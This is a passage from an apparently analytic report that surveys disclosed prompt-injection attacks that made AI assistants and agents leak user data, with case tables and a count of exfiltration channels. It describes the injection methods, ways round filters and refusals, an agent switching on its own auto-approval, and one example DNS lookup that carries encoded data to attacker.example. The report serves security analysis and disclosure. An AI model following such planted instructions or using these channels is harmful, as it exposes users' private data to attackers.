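A model's parameter count had no clear relation to its score. Rall and colleagues write that models from the same provider generally scored similarly, but their figures for Grok 4 and Grok 3 mini are far apart. They credit the good results of OpenAI's models to training that ranks developers' and users' instructions above tool output. This is plausible, but the experiment didn't test it.

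The unchanged templates succeeded most often, just over 12% of the time across all models. Disguising the instructions mostly made them harder to follow. Instructions written in Base64 reliably failed, even against small models. Radware's attack instead had plain English instructions and used Base64 only for the stolen data.

The zeros are weaker evidence of safety than they look. Rall and colleagues ran each version once and did not adapt the wording when a model refused, and many of their most effective templates were years old and publicly known. Radware's first attempts would also have scored zero, but a few rounds of adaptation raised its success rate to 100%. The high scores may not apply to commercial products, because the test agent had no protection apart from the model itself and its tool would open any address. A commercial product may have a check that blocks the tool's request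 even when the model obeys.

### Agents that operate a browser

Some agents open pages, click and type in a web browser much as a person does, often while signed in to the user's accounts. Any page they open can receive data, and it can also be an injection source if they read it.

Brave, which makes its own browser, tested two competitors, and Willison discussed the results in October 2025. Comet, the browser of the AI company Perplexity, lets users ask about a screenshot of a page. Brave put text too faint for a person to see in such an image. Comet's assistant followed the text, found the user's email address on their account page and opened an outside URL containing it. With Fellou, another AI browser, the attack only required telling the agent to visit a page. The agent followed the text on that page, opened the user's Gmail, read the subject line of a recent email and visited a URL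 containing it. Willison couldn't tell from Brave's post whether either company had fixed its flaw. PromptArmor demonstrated a similar attack in Google's Antigravity, a code editor with its own browsing agent.

Comet and Fellou run on the user's computer, so these requests leave through the user's network. An employer's firewall could at least record the hostile domain, which it could not do with Deep Research.

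In February 2025, Rehberger demonstrated a variant without a tell-tale address in Operator, an early browser agent that OpenAI ran on its own servers. Planted text in a GitHub issue could make Operator visit a site where the user was signed in, copy details such as an email address, and type them into a text box on Rehberger's page. The page sent the text to his server as Operator typed it. Operator never had to press a "submit" button, so a rule that asks the user before the agent submits a form would not have stopped this. OpenAI replaced Operator with a new agent in ChatGPT later that year.

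### A support email that reaches a programmer

Many agents now get their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting assistants to other services. A company or a hobbyist writes an "MCP server" for a service such as Jira, and any compatible assistant can then use it. Users can easily combine servers whose designers never considered how they would work together.

The security company Zenity demonstrated one such combination in 2025 with the code editor Cursor. Many companies connect their support mailbox to Jira so that each incoming email becomes a ticket. A developer may then ask Cursor to look into a ticket that a stranger wrote. In the demonstration, text in the ticket led Cursor to search the developer's code for a login token and visit a web address containing the token.

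According to Willison, Cursor at least sometimes follows the planted instructions. Cursor's makers called this a known issue and advised users to review each MCP server and connect only those that access trusted content. This left the exfiltration channel open and relied on users to keep malicious text out. Willison thinks the advice is hard to follow because attackers have so many ways to get text in front of the model.

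### Writing where the attacker can read

An agent that can post, comment or reply can leak data without contacting an outside server. In the GitHub attack that Invariant Labs demonstrated, the agent could copy private details into a public pull request because the user had given it a single access token for both public and private repositories. Invariant Labs argued that GitHub couldn't solve the problem by patching its MCP server, because each tool had worked as intended, and recommended restricting an agent to one repository per session.

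A similar chain affected Atlassian's MCP server. Willison's *Cato CTRL™ Threat Research* describes an attack in which an outside customer submits a support ticket with planted text. When an employee has an assistant process the ticket, the assistant uses the employee's access to internal data and puts what it finds into the ticket, where the attacker can read it as an ordinary support reply. Willison knew of no fix and recommended that a person confirm each reply before it goes out.

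In both cases the agent sends data only to a service that it needs for its work. An allow-list of domains would have to include GitHub or Atlassian, and a check on web addresses would find nothing unusual. The same weakness let attackers make Anthropic's Claude Cowork upload a user's files to Anthropic's own API. This method leaves more evidence, because the pull request or reply stays on the site until someone deletes it. A public pull request also exposes the data to everyone else.

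### Data inside a name lookup

ChatGPT can write Python code and run it in a container, a sealed-off Linux environment on OpenAI's servers. OpenAI says this environment can't make direct requests to the internet. In *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026), Check Point Research confirmed that ordinary attempts to reach outside servers failed, but it got data out through the Domain Name System (DNS).

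DNS translates domain names into the numeric addresses computers use to find each other. Before a program can contact attacker.example, it has to look up that name's address by querying a resolver, a server that finds addresses on behalf of other machines. If the resolver doesn't already have the address, it queries the name server responsible for the domain. The domain's owner chooses that name server and can run one that records every query it receives.

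To send the word "hello", code in the container can encode it as `nbswy3dp` and look up this name:

`nbswy3dp.attacker.example`

The resolver has no cached answer for the name, so it forwards the query to the name server for attacker.example. The attacker reads `nbswy3dp` in that server's log and decodes it. The code doesn't need a useful answer, and it never connects to the attacker's machine.

A block on web traffic didn't help because it stops a program from connecting to a website, and a DNS lookup is a separate message sent before any connection. The container sent its lookups only to its usual resolver, which passed them to the outside world. To close the gap, an operator has to turn off lookups or restrict the names that the resolver will answer for.

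Each lookup holds little data because a full domain name can have at most 253 characters, with no more than 63 between two dots. Lookups also ignore the difference between capital and small letters, which would garble Base64, so an attacker can use Base32 instead, which stores five bits in each character. With attacker.example at the end, about 233 characters remain, enough for about 145 bytes. The 300 bytes of Anna's quotation would take three lookups, which a program can make in moments.

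Check Point's attack began when the victim pasted a prompt into ChatGPT, perhaps from a web page that promised better results or free premium features. Infosecurity Magazine's *ChatGPT Security Issue Enabled Data Theft via Single Prompt* stresses that the attack depended on the user. But the attacker could also put the instructions into a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that someone configures for others to use, and then the victim only had to open it and start chatting.

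In one demonstration, a GPT acted as a personal doctor. The user uploaded laboratory results and described symptoms, and Check Point's server received the patient's name and the model's medical assessment. ChatGPT normally asks for approval before a GPT sends data to another company's service, but here it did not. When the user asked whether the data had been sent anywhere, ChatGPT said it had not. Check Point explains that the model operated as if the container could not send data out, so it did not treat the lookups as data transfers.

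DNS responses can also carry data. Check Point used them to send commands into the container, where they ran outside the chat and its safety checks. OpenAI told the researchers that it had already found the underlying problem itself, and it finished deploying a fix on 20 February 2026. Infosecurity Magazine could not establish whether anyone had exploited the flaw before then.

In eight of the twelve cases in this table, the data left inside a web address that the agent opened. In the other four, it left through text typed into a page, posts on a service the agent already used, or a DNS lookup, which contains a domain name but involves no web request.

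| Case | Injection source | Tool | Last outbound step | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT plugins, 2023 | Web page | WebPilot | Opens an address | None reported; OpenAI later retired plugins |
| ShadowLeak, 2025 | Email | Deep Research's browser tool | Opens an address | Fixed by early August 2025 |
| Comet, 2025 | Screenshot | Browser | Opens an address | Unconfirmed |
| Fellou, 2025 | Web page | Browser | Opens an address | Unconfirmed |
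| Jira to Cursor, 2025 | Support email turned into a ticket | Cursor's web access | Opens an address | None; advice to users |
| Reprompt, 2026 | Link that fills the chat box | Copilot's page fetching | Opens a series of addresses | Patched by January 2026 |
| RovoBlast, 2026 | Link that fills the chat box | Rovo's browsing agent | Opens an address | Fixed on 8 July 2026 |
| Rovo file upload, 2026 | Uploaded file | Rovo's page opener | Opens an address | Unconfirmed |
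| Operator, 2025 | GitHub issue | Browser | Types into a page | Unconfirmed; OpenAI replaced the product |
| GitHub MCP, 2025 | Public issue | GitHub connector | Opens a public pull request | No patch; advice to limit access |
| Atlassian MCP, 2025 | Support ticket | Atlassian connector | Writes to the attacker's ticket | None known; advice to confirm replies |
| ChatGPT container, 2026 | Pasted prompt or custom GPT | Python code | Looks up a domain name | Fixed on 20 February 2026 |

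## How did the same bug recur across ChatGPT, Bard, Copilot, Claude and Slack AI?

The simplest of these leaks doesn't require any agent tools. The model writes an image or link with the user's data in the address, and the app displays it. Researcher Roman Samoilenko published this attack against ChatGPT in April 2023. Over the next three years, researchers repeatedly found it in other assistants, including several from companies that had already fixed it in another product.

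### ChatGPT

*New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (Willison, 2023) describes Samoilenko's attack, in which a script on an ordinary website added the attacker's instructions to whatever a visitor copied. When the visitor pasted the text into ChatGPT, it followed the instructions and wrote a one-pixel image whose address contained data from the chat.

Rehberger reported the image leak to OpenAI on 9 April 2023. OpenAI triaged the report as "won't fix", according to Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)*. Rehberger rated the flaw "High" on CVSS, the industry's ten-point severity scale. Over the following months, OpenAI added plugins, web browsing, a code interpreter and custom GPTs to ChatGPT. Each raised the risk by giving planted text another way in or giving the model more data to leak.

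On 12 December 2023 Rehberger published a demonstration of a custom GPT that played tic-tac-toe and sent the player's conversation to his server. A press report carried by cur.at and TechRadar's *OpenAI says it has fixed a potentially serious ChatGPT flaw* both say he went public because OpenAI had not responded. His own posts describe lengthy discussions with OpenAI in April and a decision not to act, so any failure to respond must have come later.

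The leak still worked when Rehberger showed it live on a consenting victim shortly before Christmas. It mostly failed the next day, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*. Willison (2023), in a post of the same title, wrote about the change on 21 December, 256 days after the report. ChatGPT's web app now checked with an OpenAI server whether an image address was safe before loading it. Some addresses still passed, and Rehberger used them to send out the word "hi" one letter at a time.

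The check ran in the web app's code, so ChatGPT's other apps did not have it. The iPhone app was still vulnerable to the original attack that December, and OpenAI's macOS app also lacked the check when it came out in 2024. The same leak could do more harm after May 2024, when OpenAI gave ChatGPT a long-term memory, a store of notes about the user that the app adds to later conversations. Rehberger showed that planted text could add an instruction to this memory that made ChatGPT send the attacker every later conversation.

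*Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (June 2024) also describes the image problem as only partly mitigated, and says its techniques for getting past ChatGPT's safeguards would work through images too.

### Bing Chat and Claude

Microsoft received Rehberger's report on Bing Chat one day before OpenAI received his report on ChatGPT. It told him 68 days later, on 15 June 2023, that it had fixed the leak, apparently with a Content Security Policy. According to Embrace The Red, Microsoft also appeared to have put his test domain on a blocklist, so he had to move his tests elsewhere. A real attacker could get around that block by registering another domain, so the policy was the more important change.

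Anthropic was faster, confirming the leak in Claude's web app on 18 July 2023, six days after Rehberger reported it, and closing the report on 26 July, according to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*. The injection source was an uploaded file, a short biography of Einstein with instructions in the middle. Claude put a 20-word summary of the user's earlier messages into an image address, and the browser requested that address.

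Anthropic fixed the bug by replacing automatic image loading with a "Show Image" button. The image's address can still contain the user's data, so the leak now requires one click instead of none. Rehberger called the fix imperfect but agreed that it stopped the automatic theft.

Anthropic launched its Claude iPhone app in May 2024 with the same leak it had closed on the web in the summer of 2023, and fixed the app in December 2024. Willison (2024) quoted the announcement by Rehberger, who had reported the leak and said that image leaks often exist in mobile apps as well.

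### Bard

Google's chatbot Bard, now called Gemini, already had a Content Security Policy when Rehberger tested it in September 2023, just after Google had connected it to users' Gmail, Drive and Docs. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* describes how he, Joseph Thacker and Kai Greshake looked for a way to exploit these connections. A Google Doc was suitable because an attacker can share one without the victim's consent.

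Bard's policy blocked images from Rehberger's own server but allowed them from any address under google.com and googleusercontent.com. Google's Apps Script service lets anyone with a Google account run short programs on those domains and give them web addresses on script.google.com. Rehberger wrote a program that required no sign-in and saved any text added to its address to one of his Google Docs.

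The planted text in the shared document told Bard to write an image with that address and append the first 20 words of the conversation to it. The browser made the request because the destination belonged to Google. Bard was harder to manipulate than the earlier chatbots. Rehberger needed ten attempts at the wording and had to include examples of finished addresses.

He reported the flaw on 19 September. On 19 October he asked about its status, because he wanted to show the attack at a conference, and Google confirmed that it had fixed the flaw. The policy had not changed and Bard still displayed images, so he supposed that Google now filtered out addresses with data in them. The protection seems to have held for images. In *When your AI Assistant has an evil twin*, the security company WithSecure tried image-based exfiltration against Gemini and found it blocked.

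The defences against image leaks did not cover Gemini's other outbound requests. According to Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool*, another security company told Google in April 2025 that Gemini's browsing tool could send out a user's saved details and location. Google has since closed that route too.

### GitHub Copilot Chat

GitHub Copilot Chat is a Microsoft-owned programming assistant that runs in the code editor VS Code. It displayed images from any server. Rehberger put instructions in a source file comment. When a user asked Copilot to explain the file, it wrote an image whose address contained names and codes from earlier in the chat. In Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat*, he calls this very similar to his Bing Chat demonstration, which Microsoft had dealt with eight months earlier.

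He reported it on 25 February 2024. On 6 March GitHub told him that the bug was valid and already tracked internally. He asked again on 1 June, and on 12 June, 108 days after the report, GitHub confirmed a fix.

The accounts of that fix differ. Rehberger found that Copilot Chat seemed to have stopped displaying Markdown images altogether, whereas Willison, in *GitHub Copilot Chat*, describes a block on images from untrusted domains. In 2025, the researcher Omer Mayraz found a flaw that again let Copilot Chat leak data through images, exposing secrets and source code from private repositories. Underhill (2025), in *GitHub Copilot Flaw Allowed Silent Data Theft*, reports a severity score of 9.6 out of 10. GitHub turned off image rendering that August, according to the software vendor MintMCP. Some version of Copilot Chat had therefore kept displaying images after the 2024 fix, or had started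 to again.

### Slack AI

Slack AI answers questions from the messages in a company's Slack workspace. In August 2024, PromptArmor found a leak in Slack AI that used a link. Suppose a developer keeps an API key in a private channel that only she can read. An attacker with an account in the same workspace opens a public channel with no other members and plants text in it. Slack AI searches public channels even if the user has never joined them, so when the developer asks for her key, it retrieves both the message with her key and the attacker's post.

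The model then follows the instructions in the post and shows an error message with a link inviting her to sign in again. The link's address contains her key. PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* points out that the attacker needs neither access to the private channel nor knowledge of its contents. The theft is also hard to trace, because the answer cites only the developer's own channel and the attacker's post does not appear on the first page of search results.

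PromptArmor reported this on 14 August, the same day Slack AI began reading uploaded files. PromptArmor thought the change would let people outside the workspace plant text, but it had already finished its tests and did not try this.

Slack asked for more information, and PromptArmor sent videos. On 19 August Slack replied that the evidence was insufficient. It said the information in the first video came from a public channel, and all members of a workspace can search public channels by design. PromptArmor published its findings the next day so that customers could change their settings.

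Slack (2024) said on 21 August that "under very limited and specific circumstances" a person with an account in the same workspace could phish other users for certain data. It said it had deployed a patch on 20 August and had no evidence of unauthorised access to customer data. In a longer statement to ITPro (*Hackers could dupe Slack's AI features to expose private channel messages*), a spokesperson again described one user tricking another with a phishing link. Slack did not confirm to SC Media that its patch addressed PromptArmor's finding, but the statement refers to a researcher's blog post of 20 August, the day PromptArmor published.

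PromptArmor and Slack agreed that the attacker needs an account in the workspace and a click from the victim. PromptArmor's claim that an attacker could steal "anything" in a private channel goes too far, because the data has to come up in an answer to the victim's own question. Slack's word "phish" makes the flaw sound too ordinary, because a phishing message usually comes from a stranger and asks the victim to type something in. Here the link came in an answer from Slack AI and already contained the key.

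According to PromptArmor, Slack's reply of 19 August also missed the point. PromptArmor had found that a public post could control what Slack AI did with a private message. It had not objected to members being able to read public posts.

### The smaller repeats

Rehberger also found the bug in the products below. Microsoft's Azure AI Playground and the studio in Google's Vertex AI are consoles where developers try out models. Google AI Studio is a similar tool that anyone can use. Google's Colab is for writing and running Python notebooks in a browser, and NotebookLM answers questions about documents the user uploads. Amp and OpenHands are coding agents.

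| Product | Channel | Reported | Fixed | Days | What the vendor changed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Azure AI Playground (Microsoft) | Image | 24 July 2023 | 13 September 2023 | 51 | Put a space into the image Markdown so that it no longer worked |
| Vertex AI Studio (Google) | Image | 30 August 2023 | By 19 October 2023 | 50 at most | Stopped displaying images and links |
| Colab (Google) | Image | 29 November 2023 | January 2024 | 33 to 63 | Blocked the image leak; method not stated |
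| Amazon Q for Business | Link | 4 December 2023 | 29 December 2023 | 25 | Replaced addresses with a notice |
| NotebookLM (Google) | Image | 4 December 2023 | 18 April 2024 | 136 | Blocked the image leak; method not stated |
| Google AI Studio | Image | Not stated | August 2024 | Within a day of a public post | Showed the image code as text |
| Amp (Sourcegraph) | Image | 14 June 2025 | 2025 | "Quickly" | Not stated |
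| OpenHands (All Hands AI) | Image | 13 March 2025 | No fix by 9 August 2025 | Over 148 | None reported |

Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground* rates that flaw as medium severity, because the Playground could not yet fetch outside content and a victim would have had to paste in the planted text. The Vertex AI flaw had the same limit. According to Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI*, Google nevertheless accepted it as a security issue 22 minutes after Rehberger reported it, and later paid him a reward. He thinks the fix came some weeks before Google confirmed it.

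He sent the reports on Amazon Q and NotebookLM on the same day. Amazon was testing its fix by 20 December and had deployed it worldwide by the 29th, according to Embrace The Red's *AWS Fixes Data Exfiltration Attack Angle in Amazon Q for Business*. Google confirmed the NotebookLM flaw but did not fix it.

An attacker may need to control only a small part of a document, as in the NotebookLM case. In Embrace The Red's *Bobby Tables but with LLM Apps*, the victim uploads a list of customers, one of whom has put instructions in her own profile description. When the victim asks about that customer, NotebookLM sends out another customer's email address and code. The attack could also take sales figures from a separate document in the same notebook. Rehberger published after 132 days without a fix, and the Google Labs team then contacted him. Willison dates the fix to 18 April.

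Google AI Studio had leaked data through images before, and Embrace The Red's *Google AI Studio* leaves open whether the second leak was a regression or had been there all along. For the second leak, Rehberger got the model to write the image in HTML instead of Markdown. In his example, a manager uploads a set of performance reviews, and planted text in one of them makes the model send out a summary of each of the others. Google's security team gave him no date for a fix. He then tagged Logan Kilpatrick of Google in a post on X, and Google fixed the leak within 24 hours. Willison (2024), in *Google AI Studio data exfiltration demo*, noted that AI Studio was then the only place to try Google's newest model, so people were probably using it for real data as well as for development.

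A demonstration Rehberger had made long before worked unchanged on Amp. Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Amp Code* describes a second version, placed in a source file, that got the agent to read a file of passwords and keys and leak its contents. OpenHands could leak a GitHub access token in the same general way. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenHands and the Lethal Trifecta*, All Hands AI did not respond until Rehberger opened a public ticket, where the company confirmed that someone would look at his report. It did not answer his inquiry in June, and he next heard from the company on the day the post came out.

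### Grok

xAI, the maker of the chatbot Grok, disputed that the leak mattered. Rehberger, in *Security ProbLLMs in xAI's Grok*, found in late 2024 that Grok loaded images from any server when people used it in the iPhone app of the social network X. Grok on the web did not. Planted text in a picture that the user asked Grok to analyse could make it send out the conversation.

xAI at first said it could not reproduce the leak, although several other people had. A few weeks later Rehberger's demonstration stopped working, and he could not tell whether xAI had tried to fix the flaw or had changed something unrelated. He found a way around the change, and three volunteers reproduced the leak at the first attempt. Meanwhile xAI had started to put the user's name, X handle and region into Grok's standing instructions, so even a new conversation contained something to steal.

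xAI closed all his reports as "Informational", on the ground that the leak had no practical impact. He published in December 2024. One or two days later xAI changed Grok so that the first image address in a hijacked reply could no longer include the chat history or username. Grok went on loading images from any server, and Rehberger thought that data might still leak later in the conversation. In January 2025 xAI released a separate Grok app for the iPhone, which had the same flaw. Willison (2024), in *Security ProbLLMs in xAI's Grok*, wrote that xAI did not seem to be taking the problem seriously.

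In August 2026 Rony Utevsky of the security company Adversa disclosed another leak in Grok. When a user asked Grok to summarise a hostile web page, disguised instructions on the page could make it send the user's chats and personal information to the attacker. Ars Technica's *Grok exfiltrates user data when malicious instructions are encrypted* (2026) reported that the attack still worked on 20 August.

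Utevsky told The Register (*Grok chat duped into swallowing injected instructions*, 2026) that he reported the attack to xAI on 3 June, both directly and through its bug bounty programme. He said xAI acknowledged the report without saying when it would act, and that he wrote again on 4 and 10 August. SpaceX, which bought xAI earlier in 2026, did not reply to The Register. SC Media's *New attack bypasses AI guardrails by encrypting malicious prompts* (2026) mentions only that the data goes to an address the attacker controls, so the attack may not use the same image bug. It worked on the Grok website, the version that resisted Rehberger's attack in 2024.

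### Why one fix did not protect the next product

Vendors could have known about the bug, because Samoilenko and Rehberger had both made it public by the summer of 2023, before most of these reports. GitHub was already tracking it when Rehberger reported it. In Colab, he found a standing instruction not to display images, so someone at Google had probably thought of the risk. Embrace The Red's *Google Colab AI* (2024) describes how planted text overrode the instruction.

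The fixes did not spread, because most of them changed only how one app displayed replies. The model still followed planted instructions to write image addresses, and any other app that displayed its output needed its own protection. Rehberger pointed this out about ChatGPT in December 2023, and this proved true of its iPhone and macOS apps. A Content Security Policy has a similar limit. The browser receives it with the web page, so it does not protect a phone app that displays replies with its own code. Claude and Grok also leaked on the iPhone while their web versions did not.

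Rehberger suggested that OpenAI run its check on the server, where it would cover every app. He guessed that OpenAI had put the check in the web app for speed, since ChatGPT shows a reply word by word as the model writes it.

Teams within the same company also fixed the problem separately. Microsoft used a Content Security Policy in Bing Chat and a stray space in Azure AI Playground, and according to Rehberger it disabled images in GitHub Copilot Chat. Google apparently filtered addresses in Bard, dropped images and links in Vertex AI, and showed the code as text in AI Studio. These teams probably had no common display software, since the different fixes are hard to explain otherwise. That would also explain why the leak recurred in newer products from both companies. Willison reported it in Google's Antigravity in late 2025, and Microsoft's Copilot Cowork had a version of it in 2026.

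Google did not judge the reports consistently either. Both the Vertex AI and the Colab attacks required the victim to paste in planted text, but Google paid for the Vertex AI report and not for the Colab one. Rehberger takes this as a sign that the industry, and even a single company, had not yet agreed on what a safe design looks like.

The Colab report also shows how a leak that looks minor when reported can become more serious as the assistant gains access to more data. Rehberger thought the leak was low severity, but reported it because he expected Google to let the assistant read whole notebooks, which it did some months later. By then Google had closed the image leak, so a stranger's notebook could no longer use it. But Colab still displayed links and showed a confirmation page for only some of them, and Rehberger demonstrated that one click was enough to send out a user's code. ChatGPT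 and Grok also gained new features and access to new data while their leaks were still open.

The vendors of ChatGPT, NotebookLM, Google AI Studio, Slack AI and Grok acted within days of a public post. Publicity probably prompted some of these responses, most clearly at Google, where staff contacted Rehberger after one post and replied to him on X after another. Judging by the dates alone, the other vendors may already have been working on a fix. Microsoft, Anthropic, Amazon and the teams behind Bard and Vertex AI fixed their products before Rehberger published.

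Archestra, which sells security software for AI agents, argues in *Data exfiltration via Markdown image tags* (2026) that designers of each new chat product turn on Markdown for attractive headings, and that the bug is then "rediscovered from scratch". The Amp case fits this explanation, since an old attack worked there unchanged, but the GitHub case does not, because GitHub already knew about the bug.

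Rehberger attributes the bug in coding agents to some vendors relying too heavily on the model to refuse. OpenHands' model refused his first attempts to take the token but complied after he reworded the request. This shows that the refusals were weak, but not that All Hands AI was relying on them. The company's slowness to answer security reports would explain the missing fix equally well.

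## How strongly do disclosed exploits cluster on a few channels, and why?

A list of assistants that all leaked data through images can't show how common that leak is, because it includes only products that had the leak. The `exfiltration-attacks` tag on Willison's blog is a better measure because it covers injection attacks that send private data to an attacker by any route. In 2026 the tag covered 45 posts, dated April 2023 to July 2026. The count below is based on our own reading of those posts.

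### The count

An exploit counts if a post describes a particular attack that gets data out of a particular product. Seventeen posts don't qualify because they are essays, talks, notes on research or product announcements, even if they use an exploit as an example. Another post, on OpenAI's partial fix of December 2023, is excluded because an earlier post had already described the leak. The other 27 posts yield 29 exploits, because one covers two browsers and another covers two separate reports on Google's Antigravity.

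Each exploit gets one injection source and one channel, which is the last outbound step. If an agent searches a mailbox and then displays an image that contains what it found, the channel is the image. Where a post omits the source or the channel, the entry follows the researcher's own disclosure. The Claude Cowork entry takes its injection source from *The Promptware Kill Chain* (Brodt, Feldman and colleagues, 2026), which lists a Word file that the agent loaded as a "skill", a set of instructions for a task.

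| Injection source | Image | Request by the agent's tool | Clicked link | Post on a shared service | Link preview | All |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Web page | 1: Writer | 5: ChatGPT plugins, Antigravity (browser), Comet, Fellou, Claude's `web_fetch` | 0 | 0 | 1: Slack bot | 7 |
| Message, form or support ticket | 3: EchoLeak, ForcedLeak, Superhuman | 1: Jira to Cursor | 2: Microsoft 365 Copilot (2024), Slack AI | 1: Atlassian MCP | 0 | 7 |
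| File or document | 5: Bard, NotebookLM, Google AI Studio, Grok, Copilot Cowork | 1: Claude Cowork | 0 | 0 | 0 | 6 |
| Source code, or an issue on a code-hosting site | 3: GitHub Copilot Chat, GitLab Duo, Antigravity (image) | 1: Operator | 0 | 1: GitHub MCP | 0 | 5 |
| Text the user pastes | 2: ChatGPT (2023), Imprompter | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 2 |
| Not stated | 1: Claude's iPhone app | 0 | 1: Amazon Q | 0 | 0 | 2 |
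| All | 15 | 8 | 3 | 2 | 1 | 29 |

Writer is a writing assistant for companies, Superhuman is an email program, and GitLab Duo is the chatbot of a code-hosting site. Researchers gave the name EchoLeak to a leak in Microsoft 365 Copilot and ForcedLeak to one in Salesforce's Agentforce. The Imprompter attack targeted several chatbots, including Mistral's Le Chat, and relied on the user pasting in an unreadable prompt.

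Images account for 15 of the 29 exploits, and requests by the agent's tools account for another eight. Counting posts instead of exploits gives about the same proportion for images, 14 of 27. The injection sources are spread much more evenly, and no kind of source accounts for more than seven.

This contrast depends partly on how the categories are defined. Splitting files into uploads, shared documents and pictures would scatter the sources further, while grouping images, links and previews as display features would put 19 of the 29 in one category. Two entries could also be classified differently. Claude Cowork uploaded files to the attacker's account at Anthropic, which resembles a post on a shared service. The Slack entry is based on a real test of the preview but only a description of the attack on a bot.

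Whichever of these choices is made, web addresses carried the data in 25 of the 29 exploits. Usually the model wrote the data into the address, but in two cases it picked from addresses the attacker had prepared. In the 2024 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, hidden text in an email made Copilot show the user one of two links, depending on whether Microsoft's quarterly earnings had passed $53 billion, so the attacker would have learned only yes or no from a click.

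The mix of channels changed over time.

| Year of Willison's post | Image | Request by the agent's tool | Clicked link | Post on a shared service | Link preview | All |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 2023 | 3 | 1 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 4 |
| 2024 | 6 | 0 | 3 | 0 | 1 | 10 |
| 2025 | 4 | 5 | 0 | 2 | 0 | 11 |
| 2026, to July | 2 | 2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 4 |

In 2023 and 2024, 13 of the 14 exploits used a display feature, and nine of those used an image. From 2025 on, six of 15 used an image and the other nine used the agent's tools, counting posts on shared services. Researchers disclosed an image leak about every two months in the first period and about every three in the second, so most of the change comes from the increase in tool exploits. A few different choices by Willison could have reversed the fall from nine image exploits to six, but they are much less likely to have reversed the rise in tool exploits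 from one to nine.

### What the archive leaves out

The tag may have favoured image leaks at first. Willison introduced it in June 2024 as `markdown-exfiltration`, to keep track of leaks like the one in GitHub Copilot Chat, and was still using that name in January 2025. The tag now also covers older tool exploits such as the ChatGPT plugin chain, but a tool exploit from before 2025 was probably less likely to be tagged than an image leak.

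The archive undercounts both tool requests and images. It lacks ShadowLeak, Reprompt, both Rovo chains and the leak from ChatGPT's container. Adding these five would bring tool requests to 13 of 34, close behind the 15 images. But the archive also lacks at least eight image leaks, from Bing Chat in 2023 to OpenHands in 2025, and adding eight of those too would bring images to 23 of 42. It has no diagram leaks, although Cursor and Microsoft 365 Copilot each had one. Images are probably still the most common channel, but the size of their lead depends on who compiles the list.

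The archive also can't show what share of injection exploits steal data, because Willison tags only those that do. In August 2025, for example, Rehberger published a report a day on a range of AI tools in a series called *The Month of AI Bugs*. Willison's archive includes an overview of the series, but the count excludes it because it is an essay.

One report in the series concerned a flaw in GitHub Copilot that let an attacker run commands on a developer's computer. *Prompt Injection Attacks on Agentic Coding Assistants* (Maloyan and Namiot, 2026) describes how planted text in an issue or a code comment got Copilot to edit its own settings file and turn on automatic approval of tools. Copilot then ran later commands without asking the developer. Microsoft fixed this in August 2025 by requiring the user to turn on automatic approval. An attacker can do damage this way without an exfiltration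 channel, though anyone who can run commands on a computer can usually send its files out too.

Brodt and colleagues cover a wider range of outcomes in a table of 36 studies and incidents from February 2023 to January 2026, which lists the entry point and result of each. By this reference's count, 20 of the 36 end in data theft and five in code execution. The other 11 include the theft of $47,000 from a cryptocurrency wallet that an AI agent controlled and an attack that operated smart home devices. Of the eight entries for August 2025, three end in data theft and two in code execution.

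Brodt and colleagues chose prominent cases, so their 56% isn't an estimate for injection attacks in general. Their figures suggest that data theft is the most common result among well-known exploits, though not the only serious one. It may also be one of the easier results to achieve. When Maloyan and Namiot report on a test of coding editors with 314 planted instructions, data theft has the highest success rate, 84%, and attempts to gain a lasting foothold have the lowest, 41%.

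None of these works counts how often each channel occurs. Brodt and colleagues have no column for how the data left. McHugh has a field for the return channel and lists its kinds, including web requests, DNS lookups, email and posts on collaboration sites, but gives no counts.

*The Devil is in the Context* (Chang, Nikolić and colleagues, 2026) classifies injections along nine dimensions, such as whether the user can see the planted text and whether the attack changes the agent's memory, but none concerns the outbound channel. The paper applies the scheme to six public cases chosen because they differ from one another, so the mix of outcomes is weak evidence of how common each one is.

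*Talk is (Not) Cheap* (2026) comes closest to comparing injection sources with exfiltration channels. Its taxonomy, which draws on research papers, has 15 entries for injection through a data source and 11 for exfiltration of sensitive data. These totals count the kinds of attack researchers have described, however rare, so most real exploits could still use only two of the 11 kinds of exfiltration.

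Every exploit in the Willison count is a researcher's demonstration, so the count also can't show what criminals do. According to *Beyond Predictable Paths* (2026), there is a large academic literature on attacks against AI agents but few documented incidents in actual use.

In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Zhang and colleagues (2026) confirmed 15,387 planted instructions on live web pages. Only 13 aimed to steal data, nine by asking an assistant to reveal its standing instructions and four by asking for secrets. Site owners had written most of the instructions into their own pages, commonly to make scrapers produce garbage or to keep AI companies from reusing personal information. Some told visiting agents to contact an outside address. An attacker would want the same request, but here it would expose the agents as bots without stealing anything.

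Google also scanned the public web to see how much real attackers were using prompt injection, and reported the results in April 2026. According to the findings quoted in Slashdot's *Google Studies Prompt Injection Attacks Against AI Agents Browsing the Web*, a small number of injections tried to make an AI send data, including one that asked it to email the computer's login keys and list of user accounts. Google saw no significant use of the exfiltration prompts researchers published in 2025, and inferred that attackers weren't yet using this research at scale.

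These scans cover only the web. An attacker who wants a particular company's files would more likely send an email or a support ticket, which a web scan can't find. Google also didn't check social media.

### Data has to leave somehow

The simplest explanation for the clustering is that stealing data from someone else's assistant always requires a step that sends the data to the attacker. McHugh notes that ordinary output is enough when the attacker is the user, but then there is usually no one else's data to steal.

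If this is the reason, every theft should include an outbound step, and any source should work with any channel. These entries can't test the first prediction, because Willison's tag requires that the data reach the attacker. They support the second reasonably well. Images occur with all five known kinds of source, and tool requests occur with all but pasted text, which has only two entries.

There is one visible link between source and channel. Five of the eight exploits that sent data out through tool requests began on a web page, since a tool that opens pages can both bring in injected instructions and send data out.

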